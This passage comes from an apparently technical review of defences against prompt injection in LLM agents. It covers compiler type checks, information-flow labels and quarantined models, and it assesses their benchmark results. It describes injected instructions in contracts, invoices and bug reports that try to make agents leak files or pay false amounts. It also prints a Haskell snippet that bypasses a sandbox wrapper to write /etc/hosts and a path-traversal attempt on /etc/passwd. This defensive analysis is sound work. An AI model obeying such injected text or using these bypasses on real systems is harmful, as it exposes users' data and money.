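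On the same benchmark, TACIT's agents had performed no worse when writing Scala, and few of their snippets needed another attempt. The two experiments used different models. Zhao and colleagues also switched off the models' reasoning in both of their conditions, which may hurt an agent that has to write a correct program more than one that fills in the arguments of a single call.

Results for Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, a weaker model, show how much depends on coding ability. The compiler rejected 3.2% of its snippets in retail but 89% in telecom, where most of its turns made no progress. The model solved almost as few telecom tasks with ordinary tool calls, so the rejections seem to have made little difference there. In retail, its success rate was nearly nine percentage points lower than with ordinary tool calls although almost all of its code compiled, which suggests that much of that code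 was well typed but wrong.

A third benchmark, BrowseComp-Plus, has 830 hard research questions over a fixed collection of documents. DeepSeek answered 27.1% of them correctly with LACUNA, and the compiler rejected 8.6% of its snippets. Zhao and colleagues conclude that checking the code "adds no accuracy cost", but they didn't run the same models with ordinary tool calls, so the experiment can't support that conclusion.

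The researchers suspect that models write weaker Scala than Python because their training data contained less of it, and expect better prompts or additional training to help. They also deliberately chose small, inexpensive models, and larger ones would probably make fewer errors. When a model struggles with Scala, the compiler keeps the faulty code from running, but each new attempt requires another call to the model and another run of the compiler.

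## ELBA: Haskell types that record effects and the origin of data

In LACUNA, a snippet that emails a summary to Alice has the same type as one that emails it to the supplier, because both addresses are strings. ELBA, a Haskell system from the University of California San Diego, uses types to record which effects a program may have and where some of its values came from.

### One language for the whole application

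Zhou and colleagues call their approach language-based agent control. The developer writes the whole application in Haskell and calls a model through one function:

```
agent :: Defs -> Prompt -> t
```

`Defs` lists the functions and types that the model's code may use, `Prompt` is the request, and `t` is the type of result the application needs. As in LACUNA, the model's code runs only if the compiler finds that it has type `t`, and type errors go back to the model.

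LACUNA lets the model's code use any variable visible at the call. In ELBA, the code can use only the listed definitions and Haskell's basic library, so a developer can't expose the contract by leaving it in scope. Haskell is also a pure language, so the type of a computation shows whether it has effects.

### From no effects to a few

In the earlier calculator example, the model's code must have the type `Int`. Any program with an `IO` step has an `IO` type, and no permitted function turns an `IO Int` into an `Int`. The compiler therefore rejects a program that runs `rm -rf /` without having to recognise the command as dangerous, and it would also reject one that looked up today's date.

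Zhou and colleagues write that the type `Int` also rules out exceptions, but this isn't true of Haskell. *Safe Haskell* (Terei, Mazières and colleagues, 2012), the paper that introduced the restricted version of the language, states that a pure function may still throw an exception or run forever. A hostile user could make the calculator hang or return the wrong number.

Most agents need some effects, so a developer can define an effect type that permits only certain operations. Zhou and colleagues' main example is an agent that compiles a bibliography. Every entry in the file has to be a real record from DBLP, a public database of computer science papers, and not one that the model made up. In outline, the developer's library offers three functions:

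```
dblpSearch      :: String -> BibIO [DOI]
dblpFetchBib    :: DOI -> BibIO (Trusted Bib)
appendToBibFile :: Trusted Bib -> BibIO ()
```

A DOI is a paper's identification number. `BibIO X` is the type of a computation that may use these three operations and produces an `X`, while `()` stands for no result. The developer asks the model for a program of type `BibIO ()`, and an honest model might write:

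```
do dois    <- dblpSearch "prompt injection"
   entries <- mapM dblpFetchBib dois
   appendToBibFile (earliest entries)
```

Here `earliest` stands for some pure code that compares the years. The program searches, fetches every record and saves the oldest one.

Suppose the model instead tries to add a paper that doesn't exist. It could call `writeFile` from the basic library, but that function has the type `IO ()`, and the compiler accepts only `BibIO ()`. It could pass its own text to `appendToBibFile`, but that function takes a `Trusted Bib`, not a string. It could try to turn the text into a `Trusted Bib`, but that requires the constructor `Trusted`, which the library doesn't export, so the compiler rejects any program that uses it. Only `dblpFetchBib` can produce a value that `appendToBibFile` accepts.

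The effect type limits which operations the program can perform, and `Trusted` limits which values can reach those operations. The agent's code can read a trusted entry but can't make one. TypePilot's `ValidFilename` was also meant to limit which values could reach an operation, but its constructor was public and the model wrote the type itself. TACIT's `Classified` instead prevents the agent's code from looking inside a value.

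A developer could also prevent invented entries without types, by offering a single tool that both fetches and saves a record. Zhou and colleagues object that the agent could then no longer compute over the records and would have to read them one by one to find the oldest. But if a server kept the records and gave the agent's code a reference number for each, the code could compute over the records and still be unable to save an invented one. The type checker's advantage is that it finds the mistake before the program runs.

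Zhou and colleagues tested the bibliography agent on 100 computer science topics, using Claude Sonnet 5. None of its 925 citations had a wrong author, year or DOI. An ordinary agent with the same model and a web search tool got 19 of 1,002 wrong. The ordinary agent wrote its citations from search results and memory, so the experiment mainly shows that copying records is more reliable than having a model write them out. The experiment didn't include an attack or measure whether the papers suited the topic.

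### A poisoned record

`Trusted` means only that an entry came from DBLP. If an attacker gets a false record into the database, `dblpFetchBib` returns it with the same type as any other record, and the agent can save it. Similarly, if a developer marked everything in the contracts folder as trusted, the annex containing the hostile line would be marked as trusted too.

The text of a record can also carry an injection. A program written by the model can call `agent` itself, and Zhou and colleagues use this to let an agent look at a search result before it decides what to do next:

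```
do dois  <- dblpSearch "prompt injection"
   entry <- dblpFetchBib (head dois)
   agent defs ("Continue. First result: " ++ show entry)
```

The last line puts the record into the prompt of a sub-agent. If the title contains an instruction, the sub-agent's model reads it, and the type checker doesn't prevent this. But because the call is part of a `BibIO` program, Haskell infers that the sub-agent's code must have the type `BibIO ()` too. That code can't write to other files or start another sub-agent with the type `IO ()`. The first agent could instead have asked for a `Bool`, such as whether the result looks relevant, and the sub-agent's code would then have had no effects.

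With `BibIO ()`, an attacker who plants instructions in a publication database can still have the sub-agent fill the bibliography with the attacker's own papers, which may be the attacker's goal. Every call type-checks because the papers are real DBLP records.

### What Safe Haskell adds

ELBA relies on Safe Haskell to keep the model's code from bypassing ELBA's types. Besides `unsafePerformIO`, this subset of the language excludes Template Haskell, a macro system that can access constructors hidden by a module. According to the *Safe Haskell* chapter of the guide to GHC, the main Haskell compiler, functions with pure types in this subset are pure, and code can't create or examine values through constructors that a module doesn't export.

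Code in Safe Haskell may import only trusted modules. A module is trusted if the compiler has checked it under the same rules or if its author has marked it `Trustworthy`, a promise that the compiler doesn't check, much like `@assumeSafe` in Scala. An optional setting also requires the person compiling the program to name the packages whose authors they trust.

Safe Haskell doesn't forbid effects. As Terei and colleagues point out, a program in the safe subset can delete all the user's files if its type contains `IO`. To prevent this, the developer has to choose a narrower type and write a library for it without mistakes.

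GHC's own guide shows how easy it is to make one. Its example is an application that runs plugins from strangers. The type `RIO` wraps `IO`, the library offers functions that check a file's name before reading or writing it, and the constructor is hidden. But the library also exports `runRIO`, the named field that holds the wrapped action. In Haskell, code that can use a field's name can also replace the field's content, even without the constructor. A plugin could therefore apparently write:

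```
runMe = (pure ()) { runRIO = writeFile "/etc/hosts" "..." }
```

This has the required type, `RIO ()`, and skips the check on the file's name. The library could avoid the problem by exporting an ordinary function instead of the field. TACIT's public `Network` constructor was a similar mistake, and in both cases the type system worked as designed.

Zhou and colleagues say that researchers closed Haskell's loopholes long ago, but some Haskell developers have been less confident. In 2021, a participant in the mailing-list discussion *Safe Haskell?* warned that the compiler didn't guarantee the absence of `unsafeCoerce`, a function that treats a value of one type as if it had another. In the same discussion, Eisenberg (2021) wrote that he had started a proposal to remove Safe Haskell but then decided that it needed renovation instead. He compared it to a "slightly-crumbling earthen rampart"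 on two sides of a camp. In 2022, *Deprecating Safe Haskell, or heavily investing in it?* again raised the question of whether to maintain it. GHC still includes Safe Haskell, and its developers may have fixed the flaw since, but an operator who expects attacks should not treat the compiler as the only barrier.

GHC's guide also warns that Safe Haskell gives no protection during compilation, because a setting in a source file can make the compiler start another program. ELBA asks the model for a single expression, not a whole file, so there is no place for such a setting.

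### File paths as capabilities

For access to files, Zhou and colleagues define their own `RIO` type. A program of this type names files with values of type `Path`, which are capabilities for a folder or a file inside it. The application calls `evalRIO` with the name of a folder, and the model's code receives a `Path` for that folder. With the contracts folder as `root`, a program can read the contract like this:

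```
readRIO (root // "supplier.txt")
```

The operator `//` takes a path and a string and returns a narrower path. The compiler rejects `readRIO "/etc/passwd"`, because a string is not a `Path`. It accepts this program, however:

```
readRIO (root // "../../etc/passwd")
```

ELBA checks the path at run time, not at compile time. The `//` operator resolves the dots and any symbolic links in the string, finds that the result is outside the folder, and fails before `readRIO` opens anything. TACIT also checks paths at run time, but its snippets specify the folder themselves. An ELBA snippet can't call `evalRIO` to gain access to another folder, because `evalRIO` returns an `IO` computation and the snippet must have the type `RIO`.

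Zhou and colleagues compare this with coding agents that check shell commands against lists of forbidden patterns. In March 2026, a bug in Claude Code let compound commands past its deny list because the program checked only the part before the first `&&`. An agent can also hide a forbidden file name inside a short Python program that it runs from the shell. ELBA's interface has no shell, so it has no command strings to parse. Zhou and colleagues consider operating-system sandboxes a useful addition because these still work if the language's protections fail.

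With access limited to the contracts folder, the injected snippet can't email the contract or run a web search. It can still overwrite the signed contract with an altered one, because the same `Path` works for reading and writing. A developer could prevent this by defining separate types for files the agent may read and files it may change.

### Labels that LIO checks at run time

An assistant that needs both the contract and the web also needs rules about where data may go. ELBA handles these with LIO, an existing Haskell library for information-flow control. LIO labels data with who may see it and which sources influenced it. A running program also has a current label, which covers everything it has read so far.

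Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, use a simpler kind of label for their own agent language, and the same rules are easier to see there. A label is a set that may contain S for secret and U for untrusted. If the current label is C, then:

- reading data with label L changes the current label to C ∪ L;
- writing to a destination that accepts the label D is allowed only if C ⊆ D.

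The program starts with an empty label. The contract is secret and an outsider wrote it, so reading it changes the current label to {S, U}. A search engine may receive text from anyone but no secrets, so it accepts {U}. Since {S, U} is not a subset of {U}, LIO stops any search after the program reads the contract, whatever the query contains. The file with the signed contract may hold secrets but no untrusted text, so it accepts {S}, and LIO also stops the attempt to overwrite that file.

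ELBA checks all of this at run time, not at compile time. A program that reads the contract and then searches the web has the type `DC ()`, where `DC` is the effect type for computations under LIO. A program that searches first and then reads has the same type. Both compile, and LIO stops the first one while it is running, which is too late to recall any message it sent before reading the contract. The compiler does ensure that the model's code performs every effect through LIO, since a program with a plain `IO` action in it would have the wrong type.

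A program that has read one untrusted page could soon do nothing useful, so LIO has a function called `toLabeled`. It runs part of a program separately and returns the result in a labelled wrapper, and the current label of the main program stays as it was. A sub-agent inside `toLabeled` resembles the quarantined model in Willison's arrangement, except that it may use tools as long as its own label permits. Zhou and colleagues give the example of a sub-agent that opens an email at an address supplied by an outsider and drafts a message about it. The main agent then sends the draft with this function:

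```
sendDM :: User -> Labeled DCLabel Message -> DC ()
```

The recipient is a plain value and the message is labelled. `sendDM` first checks that the main program has read nothing untrusted, because an attacker could otherwise have chosen the recipient. It then uses its own privilege to release the text of the message.

With an email function of this kind, ELBA can handle the case that LACUNA's types couldn't. The main agent, which has read only the user's request, chooses Alice as the recipient. A sub-agent reads the contract and writes the summary. If the hostile line causes the sub-agent to try to send the summary to the supplier, the email function blocks the email because the sub-agent's label contains U. This doesn't work if the right address appears only in the contract, because the main agent would have to read untrusted text to find it.

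The summary that reaches Alice can still be false. A strict policy could block any text that the contract had influenced, but then nobody would get a summary.

### What the theorem guarantees

Zhou and colleagues prove that adding a model to a typed language doesn't weaken what its types guarantee. They call the language L and describe a program e by traces(e), the set of all sequences of tool calls with visible side effects that it can produce. A property P belongs to a type t if every program of that type has it:

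⊢ e : t ⟹ P(traces(e))

The notation ⊢ e : t means that e has the type t. For the type `RIO ()`, P could be the property that no call accesses a file outside the folder. The language L_agent is L with the function `agent` added. By the theorem, every such property of L also holds in L_agent.

The proof replaces each call to `agent` with an ordinary function written in L. This function requests a program from the model, checks its type, and either runs it or reports failure. Since the model's program may call `agent` again, each call has a level that limits how deeply further calls can nest. At level 0, the original call and its replacement both fail without doing anything. At level n + 1, both get the same program from the model, and any calls in that program have a level of at most n, where the two versions behave alike by induction. The rewritten program therefore has the same traces as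 the original. It is also a well-typed program in L, so P holds for it and hence for the original.

The theorem assumes nothing about the quality of the model, which an attacker may control. But it only carries over properties that L already has, so any gap in GHC or in a developer's library carries over too. The theorem also covers only tool calls. A trace does not include queries to the model, although the model's provider can read the prompt, which may contain the full text of the contract.

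The proof assumes that the model always gives the same answer to the same prompt. Zhou and colleagues consider randomness irrelevant to the properties they study. That is true of a rule about files, which has to hold for every possible answer. It is less clear for information flow, because a standard way to show that a secret doesn't leak is to compare two runs that differ only in the secret, and with a random model the runs may differ even if the secret has no effect. Garby and colleagues therefore state the guarantee for their own language in terms of probabilities, and a computer has checked their proof. They note that neither ELBA nor TACIT has a machine-checked theorem about the complete agent system.

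### Attacks on AgentDojo

Zhou and colleagues tested ELBA on AgentDojo's Slack domain, with 21 user tasks and 5 injection tasks. They compared it with CaMeL, which separates the planning model from the data and enforces its policies at run time. They ran both systems with and without policies on Claude Opus 4.7, Claude Opus 4.8, Claude Sonnet 5 and GPT-5.4. Without policies, ELBA still checked types, but the Slack functions had the plain type `IO`.

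All four models resisted all 105 stock attacks in both systems, even without policies, so results on these attacks don't measure the value of types or labels.

The researchers then simulated an attacker who always succeeds. In ELBA, only sub-agents read outside data, and their prompts normally contain a task and the data. Whenever the data contained an injection, the modified version deleted the task, so that the sub-agent received the attacker's text as its only instruction. Each model had 735 runs:

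| | Opus 4.7 | Opus 4.8 | GPT-5.4 | Sonnet 5 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Successful injections without policies | 310 | 275 | 65 | 195 |
| Successful injections with policies | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| User tasks completed without policies | 523 | 557 | 256 | 494 |
| User tasks completed with policies | 351 | 312 | 290 | 294 |

With policies in place, AgentDojo counted 28 attacks as successful because the agent opened a web address that the attacker had named. Zhou and colleagues checked these runs by hand and excluded them, because the address carried no data and the policies allow such a visit. That is reasonable, although the attacker learns from the visit that an agent has read the message.

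This is better evidence than the TACIT and LACUNA experiments provide, because it doesn't depend on whether the model falls for the injection. Garby and colleagues note that many attacks on systems like CaMeL fail simply because the model plans its actions before it reads any hostile text. ELBA lets the model write new code after reading, so its defence relies on enforcement alone. But the attacks were stock injections. An attacker who knew the policies would try something they permit, such as putting a false statement in a message the user wants to send.

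Static type checking probably blocked few of these attacks directly. The compiler checked the model's code both with and without policies, and 845 of 2,940 injections succeeded without them. With policies, the functions went through LIO, which blocks forbidden actions at run time. The types kept the hijacked code from bypassing LIO, but the experiment doesn't show how often that code contained an attempt to do so.

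### Is ELBA more useful than CaMeL?

Zhou and colleagues report that ELBA completes roughly twice as many tasks as CaMeL with policies on, and about 15% more with policies off. Added up over the four models, the user tasks completed in the ordinary tests come to:

| | Without attack, of 84 | Under three kinds of stock attack, of 1,260 |
|---|---|---|
| ELBA with policies | 37 (44%) | 571 (45%) |
| CaMeL with policies | 20 (24%) | 303 (24%) |
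| ELBA without policies | 64 (76%) | 1,017 (81%) |
| CaMeL without policies | 61 (73%) | 870 (69%) |

With policies on, ELBA did better than CaMeL in all 16 combinations of model and attack setting. But every combination uses the same 21 tasks from one of AgentDojo's four domains, so the large totals make the comparison look more precise than it is. An earlier version of the paper, which called the system TypeGuard, claimed only that its utility was comparable to CaMeL's. In that version, TypeGuard completed 8 of the 21 tasks and CaMeL completed 7, and the confidence intervals for the difference all included zero.

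The two systems also enforced different policies. Zhou and colleagues wrote new ones for ELBA, under which an agent that reads untrusted data keeps only the privileges of the data's source. ELBA's lead may come partly from its design, since a sub-agent can react to what it reads and use tools, and partly from rules that permit more. Running both systems under the same policy would separate these effects, and the researchers suggest standard policies as future work. They also didn't run the test with hijacked sub-agents on CaMeL, though they expect its design would resist the attack.

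Even in ELBA, the policies greatly reduce utility. Without an attack, the agents completed 64 tasks with policies off and 37 with policies on. Some of the lost tasks can't be done safely under any strict rule, just as an assistant can't look up the companies in a secret contract without telling the search engine their names. Garby and colleagues recommend explicit exceptions, in which a program marks a specific piece of untrusted data as acceptable. With such exceptions, their own agent kept most of its utility on AgentDojo's banking tasks. Attacks succeeded in two of 1,296 runs, both times because the agent had accepted a file with payment instructions that the attacker had replaced.

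The models had little trouble writing Haskell. ELBA averaged 0.13 retries per run, and a model failed to produce well-typed code within the limit in only 7 of 2,688 runs. These models are larger than the ones that struggled with Scala in LACUNA. ELBA took about three times as long as CaMeL, mainly because it calls the model again whenever the agent has to react to new data.

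## Type-directed privilege separation: limiting what the model reads

TACIT, LACUNA and ELBA check the program that a model writes, possibly after the model has read hostile text. Jacob and colleagues instead apply types to what the model reads. Their method, type-directed privilege separation, keeps Willison's split between a quarantined model that reads untrusted text and a privileged model that chooses the actions. But it lets the privileged model read the quarantined model's reply if it consists of numbers, yes-or-no answers or choices from a fixed list.

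For the supplier's contract, the privileged model could receive `true` for whether there is a penalty clause and `90` for the notice period in days, without reading any of the contract. The hostile line in the annex may still take over the quarantined model, but that model's reply has no field that could hold an order to send the file to an outside address.

### Four types and no strings

Jacob and colleagues permit four types:

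| Type | Possible values | Why it can't carry an instruction |
|---|---|---|
| `int` | whole numbers | An instruction needs some free text, and a number contains none |
| `float` | decimal numbers | There are more of them, but they are still only numbers |
| `bool` | true or false | It does the same job as the integers 0 and 1 |
| `enum` | one text from a fixed set | The developer has checked every text in the set beforehand |

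A reply, called a handoff, can contain several values in an array or object, as long as each field has one of these types. The quarantined model can also store free text in a variable that the privileged model passes on without reading.

A string would let an attacker put their own words next to the user's request, while an `enum` allows only options written by the developer. If the options for a document are `invoice`, `contract` and `other`, an attacker can at most cause the wrong one to appear. But the developer has to write the options without using untrusted text. If an email assistant took its options from the subject lines in the inbox, anyone could add an option by sending an email.

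Numbers are less safe than the table suggests, because a long enough integer can encode any text. At two digits per letter, 200 digits can encode 100 letters. The privileged model would have to recognise the code and then obey the decoded text, which is unlikely but hard to rule out. Jacob and colleagues limit the length of arrays to prevent such "decoding attacks". Developers should limit the size of each number for the same reason.

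A choice among n values carries at most log₂ n bits of information: 1 bit for a `bool`, about 3.5 bits for a whole number from 0 to 10, and 64 bits, or eight characters of ordinary text, for a standard large integer. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025) presents FIDES, an agent whose security labels use this idea. The labels record a value's type as well as its source, and they rank `bool` below `enum` and `enum` below `string`. A policy can then let the agent act on an untrusted `bool` but not on an untrusted string. The FIDES experiments didn't include this feature because most tasks in AgentDojo didn't need it.

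### A check on data at run time

Despite the method's name, no compiler checks the privileged model's code. The check applies to data, and it happens while the agent is running, each time the quarantined model replies. The developer writes a schema that lists the fields and their types, for example:

```
amount_cents: integer from 0 to 10000000
currency:     "EUR", "USD" or "GBP"
```

To enforce the schema, Jacob and colleagues use structured outputs, a feature that most model providers offer. Like the TypeScript constraint of Mündler and colleagues, this feature prevents the model from producing a token that would break the required format. *SPA* (2026) describes a similar arrangement, in which the quarantined model has no tools and each of its steps has its own schema.

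The trusted base therefore includes the schema, the provider's enforcement of it, and the program that carries values from one model to the other. A schema with a string field would give no protection, even if the provider enforced it just as reliably. If a connecting program written in Python mistakenly puts the whole invoice into the privileged model's prompt, it will run without an error.

### An invoice with a false amount

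Suppose a user asks an assistant to pay a supplier's latest invoice, which is for 420 euros. An attacker has added a line to the invoice telling AI assistants to forward the user's mailbox to an outside address and to report the total as 4,200 euros.

1. The quarantined model reads the invoice, including the added line, and obeys it.
2. The schema allows one integer, the amount in cents, so the reply can't mention the mailbox.
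3. The quarantined model replies `420000`, which is an integer, and the check accepts it.
4. The privileged model, which has read only the user's request and this number, pays 4,200 euros to the account in the user's address book.

The mailbox is safe, but the user has paid ten times the correct amount. The attacker can no longer choose which action the agent takes but can still set a value that the action uses. The type can't prevent this, because `42000` and `420000` are both integers.

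Sometimes a value also decides which action the agent takes. If the user had told the agent to pay invoices under 1,000 euros and ask about larger ones, an attacker could use a false total of 900 euros to get paid without the agent asking the user. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* describes an agent that picks its next task from a list containing `schedule_meeting`, `out_of_office_reply` and `forward_email`. An attacker who controls the answer can choose `forward_email`, even though he can't write an instruction. Developers should therefore include only options that would do little harm if the agent chose them wrongly.

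Dongol (2026), in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, makes the same distinction between actions and values in a formal model of agents. If an agent fixes its plan before any model reads untrusted text, and a quarantined model answers its questions, an injection can only corrupt an answer, not add a call to the plan. But Dongol assumes that the attacker can freely choose the answer and make it depend on any secret in the question. If the question about the invoice also contained the user's credit limit, the quarantined model could return the limit as the amount due, and the supplier would learn it from the payment.

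Dongol's proofs concern leaks, so they don't cover a payment that is wrong but leaks nothing. They also don't cover agents that choose each call as they go. In Jacob and colleagues' method, the privileged model may choose its next step after reading a handoff. This makes it more flexible than an agent with a fixed plan, but it also gives a false value more influence over what the model does.

One remedy is to restrict where a value may come from. For tools that change something, *CapLite* (2026) treats most arguments, including amounts and recipients, as matters of authority and accepts only values stated in the user's request. If the request were "Pay the supplier 420 euros", the agent could pay that amount but not the false total. "Pay the latest invoice" contains no amount, so the agent would have to ask the user or give up. *CapLite* leaves free text, such as the body of a message, unrestricted.

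Garby and colleagues considered a rule that would let their agent trust a value from an untrusted file only if it belonged to a short fixed list. The rule suits yes-or-no answers and categories, but it would reject account numbers and payment amounts, which the agent needs most in banking tasks. They conclude that the user's decision to delegate justifies trusting such a value, because someone who asks an agent to pay the bill in a file has authorised it to rely on that file. That is a fair account of responsibility, but the user probably didn't mean to authorise whatever an attacker wrote there.

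### Shopping and scheduling

Jacob and colleagues built three agents for tasks in which the privileged model has to learn something from untrusted text, and tested each with and without the defence:

| | Model | Attacks succeeded, undefended | Attacks succeeded, defended | Tasks completed, undefended | Tasks completed, defended |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Online shopping | GPT-4o | 31.7% | 0.0% | 21.8% | 22.4% |
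| Calendar scheduling | GPT-4o | 63.0% | 0.0% | 90.0% | 91.0% |
| Bug fixing | GPT-5.2 | 98.9% | 0.0% | 68.3% | 45.0% |

The figures for completed tasks come from runs without an attack.

For each of 500 requests, the shopping agent looked for a matching product in WebShop, a simulated store with about 1.2 million products. WebShop has no reviews, so the researchers had GPT-4o write some. To attack the agent, they added a message to one review of the right product, claiming that the item was a banned substance and that the agent had to leave the page at once.

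In the defended version, the quarantined model converted each review into two integers from 0 to 10, rating how strongly the review supported the product and how relevant it was. The privileged model received the median of each score and the number of reviews. The median also gives some protection against false scores, because a single hostile review barely moves it when there are many others. An attacker who writes most of the reviews controls the median, but fake reviews on that scale would also mislead human shoppers.

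Jacob and colleagues treated only the reviews as untrusted, so the privileged model still read the rest of the page, including the product description. In a real marketplace, a stranger may have written the description as well, and an instruction in it would reach the privileged model as plain text.

The calendar agent arranged meetings by email between 100 pairs of simulated people. In the attack, the other person answered every email with a request for the user's whole calendar, including the private descriptions of events. The undefended agent sent private information in 63 of the 100 conversations. In the defended version, the quarantined model reduced the emails to a list of one-hour slots from a fixed set. The privileged model compared these slots with the user's calendar, and a separate model that had never seen the other person's emails wrote the reply.

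The other person can still suggest one slot after another and work out from the refusals when the user is busy. Dongol would not count this as a leak caused by injection, because an honest request for a meeting reveals the same busy hours. His criterion compares the agent with a reference agent whose model never obeys untrusted text, and counts only information that the reference agent would not have revealed.

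The defence did not measurably reduce either agent's utility. The zeros in the table are weaker evidence. Jacob and colleagues regard the security as guaranteed by design, so they expected the zeros and measured only to confirm them. They also used the same attacks on the defended and undefended agents. Each attack demanded an action, such as leaving a page or sending a calendar, and none aimed to produce a false score or time slot. An attacker who understood the defence would try that, although it falls outside Jacob and colleagues' definition of prompt injection, which excludes misinformation.

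### Fixing a bug without reading the report

Jacob and colleagues tested the bug-fixing agent on 180 real issues from SWE-bench Lite. It fixed 123 without the defence and 81 with it, a drop of about a third. For the attack, they added a sentence to each bug report asking the agent to create an unrelated file called `pipipi.py`. The undefended agent created the file in 178 of 180 cases.

The defended agent needed a much longer process:

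1. The quarantined agent reads the bug report, explores a copy of the code and fills in a handoff. It picks one of about fifty categories of bug, such as "off-by-one bug" or "race condition", and one of three sizes for the fix. It then lists suspicious regions of code, each with a file number, a first and last line, and a role, such as "region suspected to contain the bug".
2. A planner, which sees the handoff and a clean copy of the code but not the report, writes three plans for a fix in ordinary English.
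3. A quarantined judge, which has read the report, compares the plans and returns the number of the best one.
4. The privileged agent receives the handoff and that plan, and writes the fix.

The third step lets the privileged agent read a whole plan in English despite the ban on free text. The plan was written by a model that had never been given the report, and the attacker can influence only the handoff and the choice among three plans.

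Even so, the handoff omits much of what a bug report often contains, such as an error message, an example that triggers the bug and a description of the correct behaviour. The handoff can record that lines 40 to 52 of a file contain a wrong return value, but not what the function should return, so the planner has to guess this from the code. Jacob and colleagues also attribute the loss to the importance of natural language in these reports. They had already removed feature requests from the test set, and those would probably have been harder still, because a list of line numbers can't describe a feature that doesn't exist yet.

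The researchers argue that 45.0% is still substantial, since an older model, Claude Sonnet 3.7, scores 48.0% on SWE-bench Lite without a defence. But an operator deciding whether to use the defence would compare it with the same model undefended, which fixed about 50% more bugs. Designing the handoff also took considerable testing on a separate set of issues, and a developer would have to repeat that work for each new kind of task.

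The quarantined agent in this experiment can run shell commands, unlike Willison's quarantined model, which has no tools. Jacob and colleagues write that no harm follows if an attacker takes over this agent, because it can't control the privileged agent's actions. This is true only if the quarantined agent's container holds no secrets and has no way to send them out. The experiment measured an attack success rate of zero, but it didn't test this condition because it counted only unwanted files in the final patch. An attacker could also use the typed fields to direct the privileged agent to working code, for example by reporting a login check as an "incorrect conditional logic" bug.

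How often agents need untrusted text to decide what to do depends on the kind of work. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* classifies an AgentDojo task as data dependent if no single sequence of tool calls and final answer is correct for all possible data. Of the 97 tasks, 20 are data dependent. The share is 5% for workspace tasks, 10% for travel tasks, and about 43% for banking and Slack tasks.

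A `bool` is enough for some tasks. Suppose the user asks the agent to read three emails and create a calendar event if one of them proposes a meeting. FIDES can use its quarantined model to check for a proposal, and the planning model reads only the yes-or-no result. If the result is yes, the quarantined model extracts the time and participants into a variable, which goes straight to the calendar without the planning model reading it. An attacker who wrote one of the emails can still get a fake meeting added to the calendar, but can't make the planning model delete a file.

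Other tasks have no such short answer. If a user tells a coding agent to set up a project by following its README, the instructions in the file are the task, and no developer could list them all in advance. Wang, Li and colleagues (2026), in *The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents*, argue that existing benchmarks contain too few tasks in which the agent has to act on what it finds, so defences that hide or discard outside text look more useful than they are. They built a benchmark, AgentPI, around five kinds of such tasks and tested eight defences. None combined trustworthy protection with high utility and low delay.

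### Typed answers inside checked programs

Typed input and a type check on generated code protect against different failures, and an agent can use both. ELBA comes closest to doing so. Zhou and colleagues give the example of a program that sorts dates written in various formats and has a sub-agent parse each one. Haskell infers from the sorting function that every answer must be a `Date`, so the sub-agent can't return a string containing an instruction.

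The invoice could work the same way:

```
do text <- readInvoice
   let cents = agent basics ("Total in cents:\n" ++ text) :: Int
   agent payments ("Pay the supplier, in cents: " ++ show cents)
```

The first sub-agent reads the invoice, but its code can produce only a number. The second reads that number and writes the payment code, which may use only the functions in `payments`.

A developer may overlook a source of hostile text, such as the product descriptions in the shopping experiment. The second model may then write malicious code, but the compiler still limits what that code can do. If the developer instead grants the code too much access, as in TACIT's simulated bank, where every snippet could call `sendMoney`, the compiler would accept a malicious payment. However, the model that writes the payment code has read no instruction to make one.

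LACUNA allows a similar design. The earlier gap listed the companies in a contract as strings. If it instead had type `agent[Boolean]` and checked whether the contract names a particular company, its result could not carry an instruction into the next prompt.

However, neither compiler enforces the rule about input by itself. In the Haskell program above, a developer could write `text` in place of `show cents`, and the program would still compile, because the prompt and the invoice are both strings. ELBA's labels can catch some consequences of this mistake at run time. To catch it at compile time, a developer could give outside text its own type, say `Untrusted`, with no way to turn it into a string. The only functions that accept it would query a quarantined model about it and return a number, a `bool` or a choice from a list. Code that put the invoice into a privileged prompt would then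 fail to compile. This would amount to TACIT's wrapper, modified to let only typed answers out, but nobody seems to have tested it.

The false total of 4,200 euros would pass all of these checks. A developer can reduce the damage with a type `Amount`, whose hidden constructor rejects any value above a limit the user has set, and a payment function that accepts only `Amount` values. With a limit of 500 euros, the attacker could still overcharge the user by up to 80 euros.

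## CaMeL: checks at run time instead of compile time

TACIT, LACUNA and ELBA reject some programs before they start. CaMeL instead runs the program and checks each tool call just before it happens. Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues from Google DeepMind and ETH Zurich presented it in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). CaMeL keeps Willison's split between a privileged model that acts and a quarantined model that reads, but replaces his controller with an interpreter that tracks where every value came from.

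### One email request

Suppose a user asks the assistant to email Alice a summary of the supplier's contract. The privileged model sees this request and the descriptions of the tools. It writes a plan in a restricted version of Python, along these lines:

```
contract = read_file("supplier.txt")
summary = ask_quarantined("Summarise this contract", contract)
alice = find_contact("Alice")
send_email(alice, "Contract", summary)
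```

1. The privileged model writes all four lines before anyone opens the contract, so the hostile line in the annex can't affect them.
2. The interpreter reads the file and labels the text. The label records that the text came from the supplier and that only the user and Alice may read it.
3. The quarantined model reads the text and may obey the hostile line. But it has no tools, and the interpreter stores whatever it returns in `summary`, with the contract's label.
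4. The interpreter looks up Alice in the address book and labels her address as coming from there.
5. Before `send_email` runs, the interpreter checks the policy for emails. A sensible policy requires an address from a trusted source and a recipient who may read the text. Both conditions hold, so the email leaves.

The CaMeL paper calls these labels capabilities, although they describe data and don't give code permission to do anything. Under the usual rule, which *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* sets out, a value that depends on several others gets the union of their sources and the intersection of their readers. If A, B and C may read one document and B, C and D may read another, only B and C may read a text that draws on both.

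LACUNA's compiler couldn't distinguish Alice's address from the supplier's, because both are strings. CaMeL's interpreter has the actual address and its label. If the user had asked to send the summary to the contact person named in the contract, the quarantined model would have extracted the address, and its label would have shown that it came from the supplier. CaMeL could then ask the user to approve the email. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) objects that such requests tire users and give the attacker a chance to deceive them.

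The summary that Alice receives may still be false. CaMeL's developers explicitly exclude attacks that only change text.

### How CaMeL did on AgentDojo

CaMeL completed 77% of AgentDojo's tasks under attack, compared with 84% for an undefended agent, according to Narisetty and colleagues' summary of the original results. No injection within its threat model succeeded. CaMeL used about 2.8 times as many input tokens and 2.7 times as many output tokens as the undefended agent.

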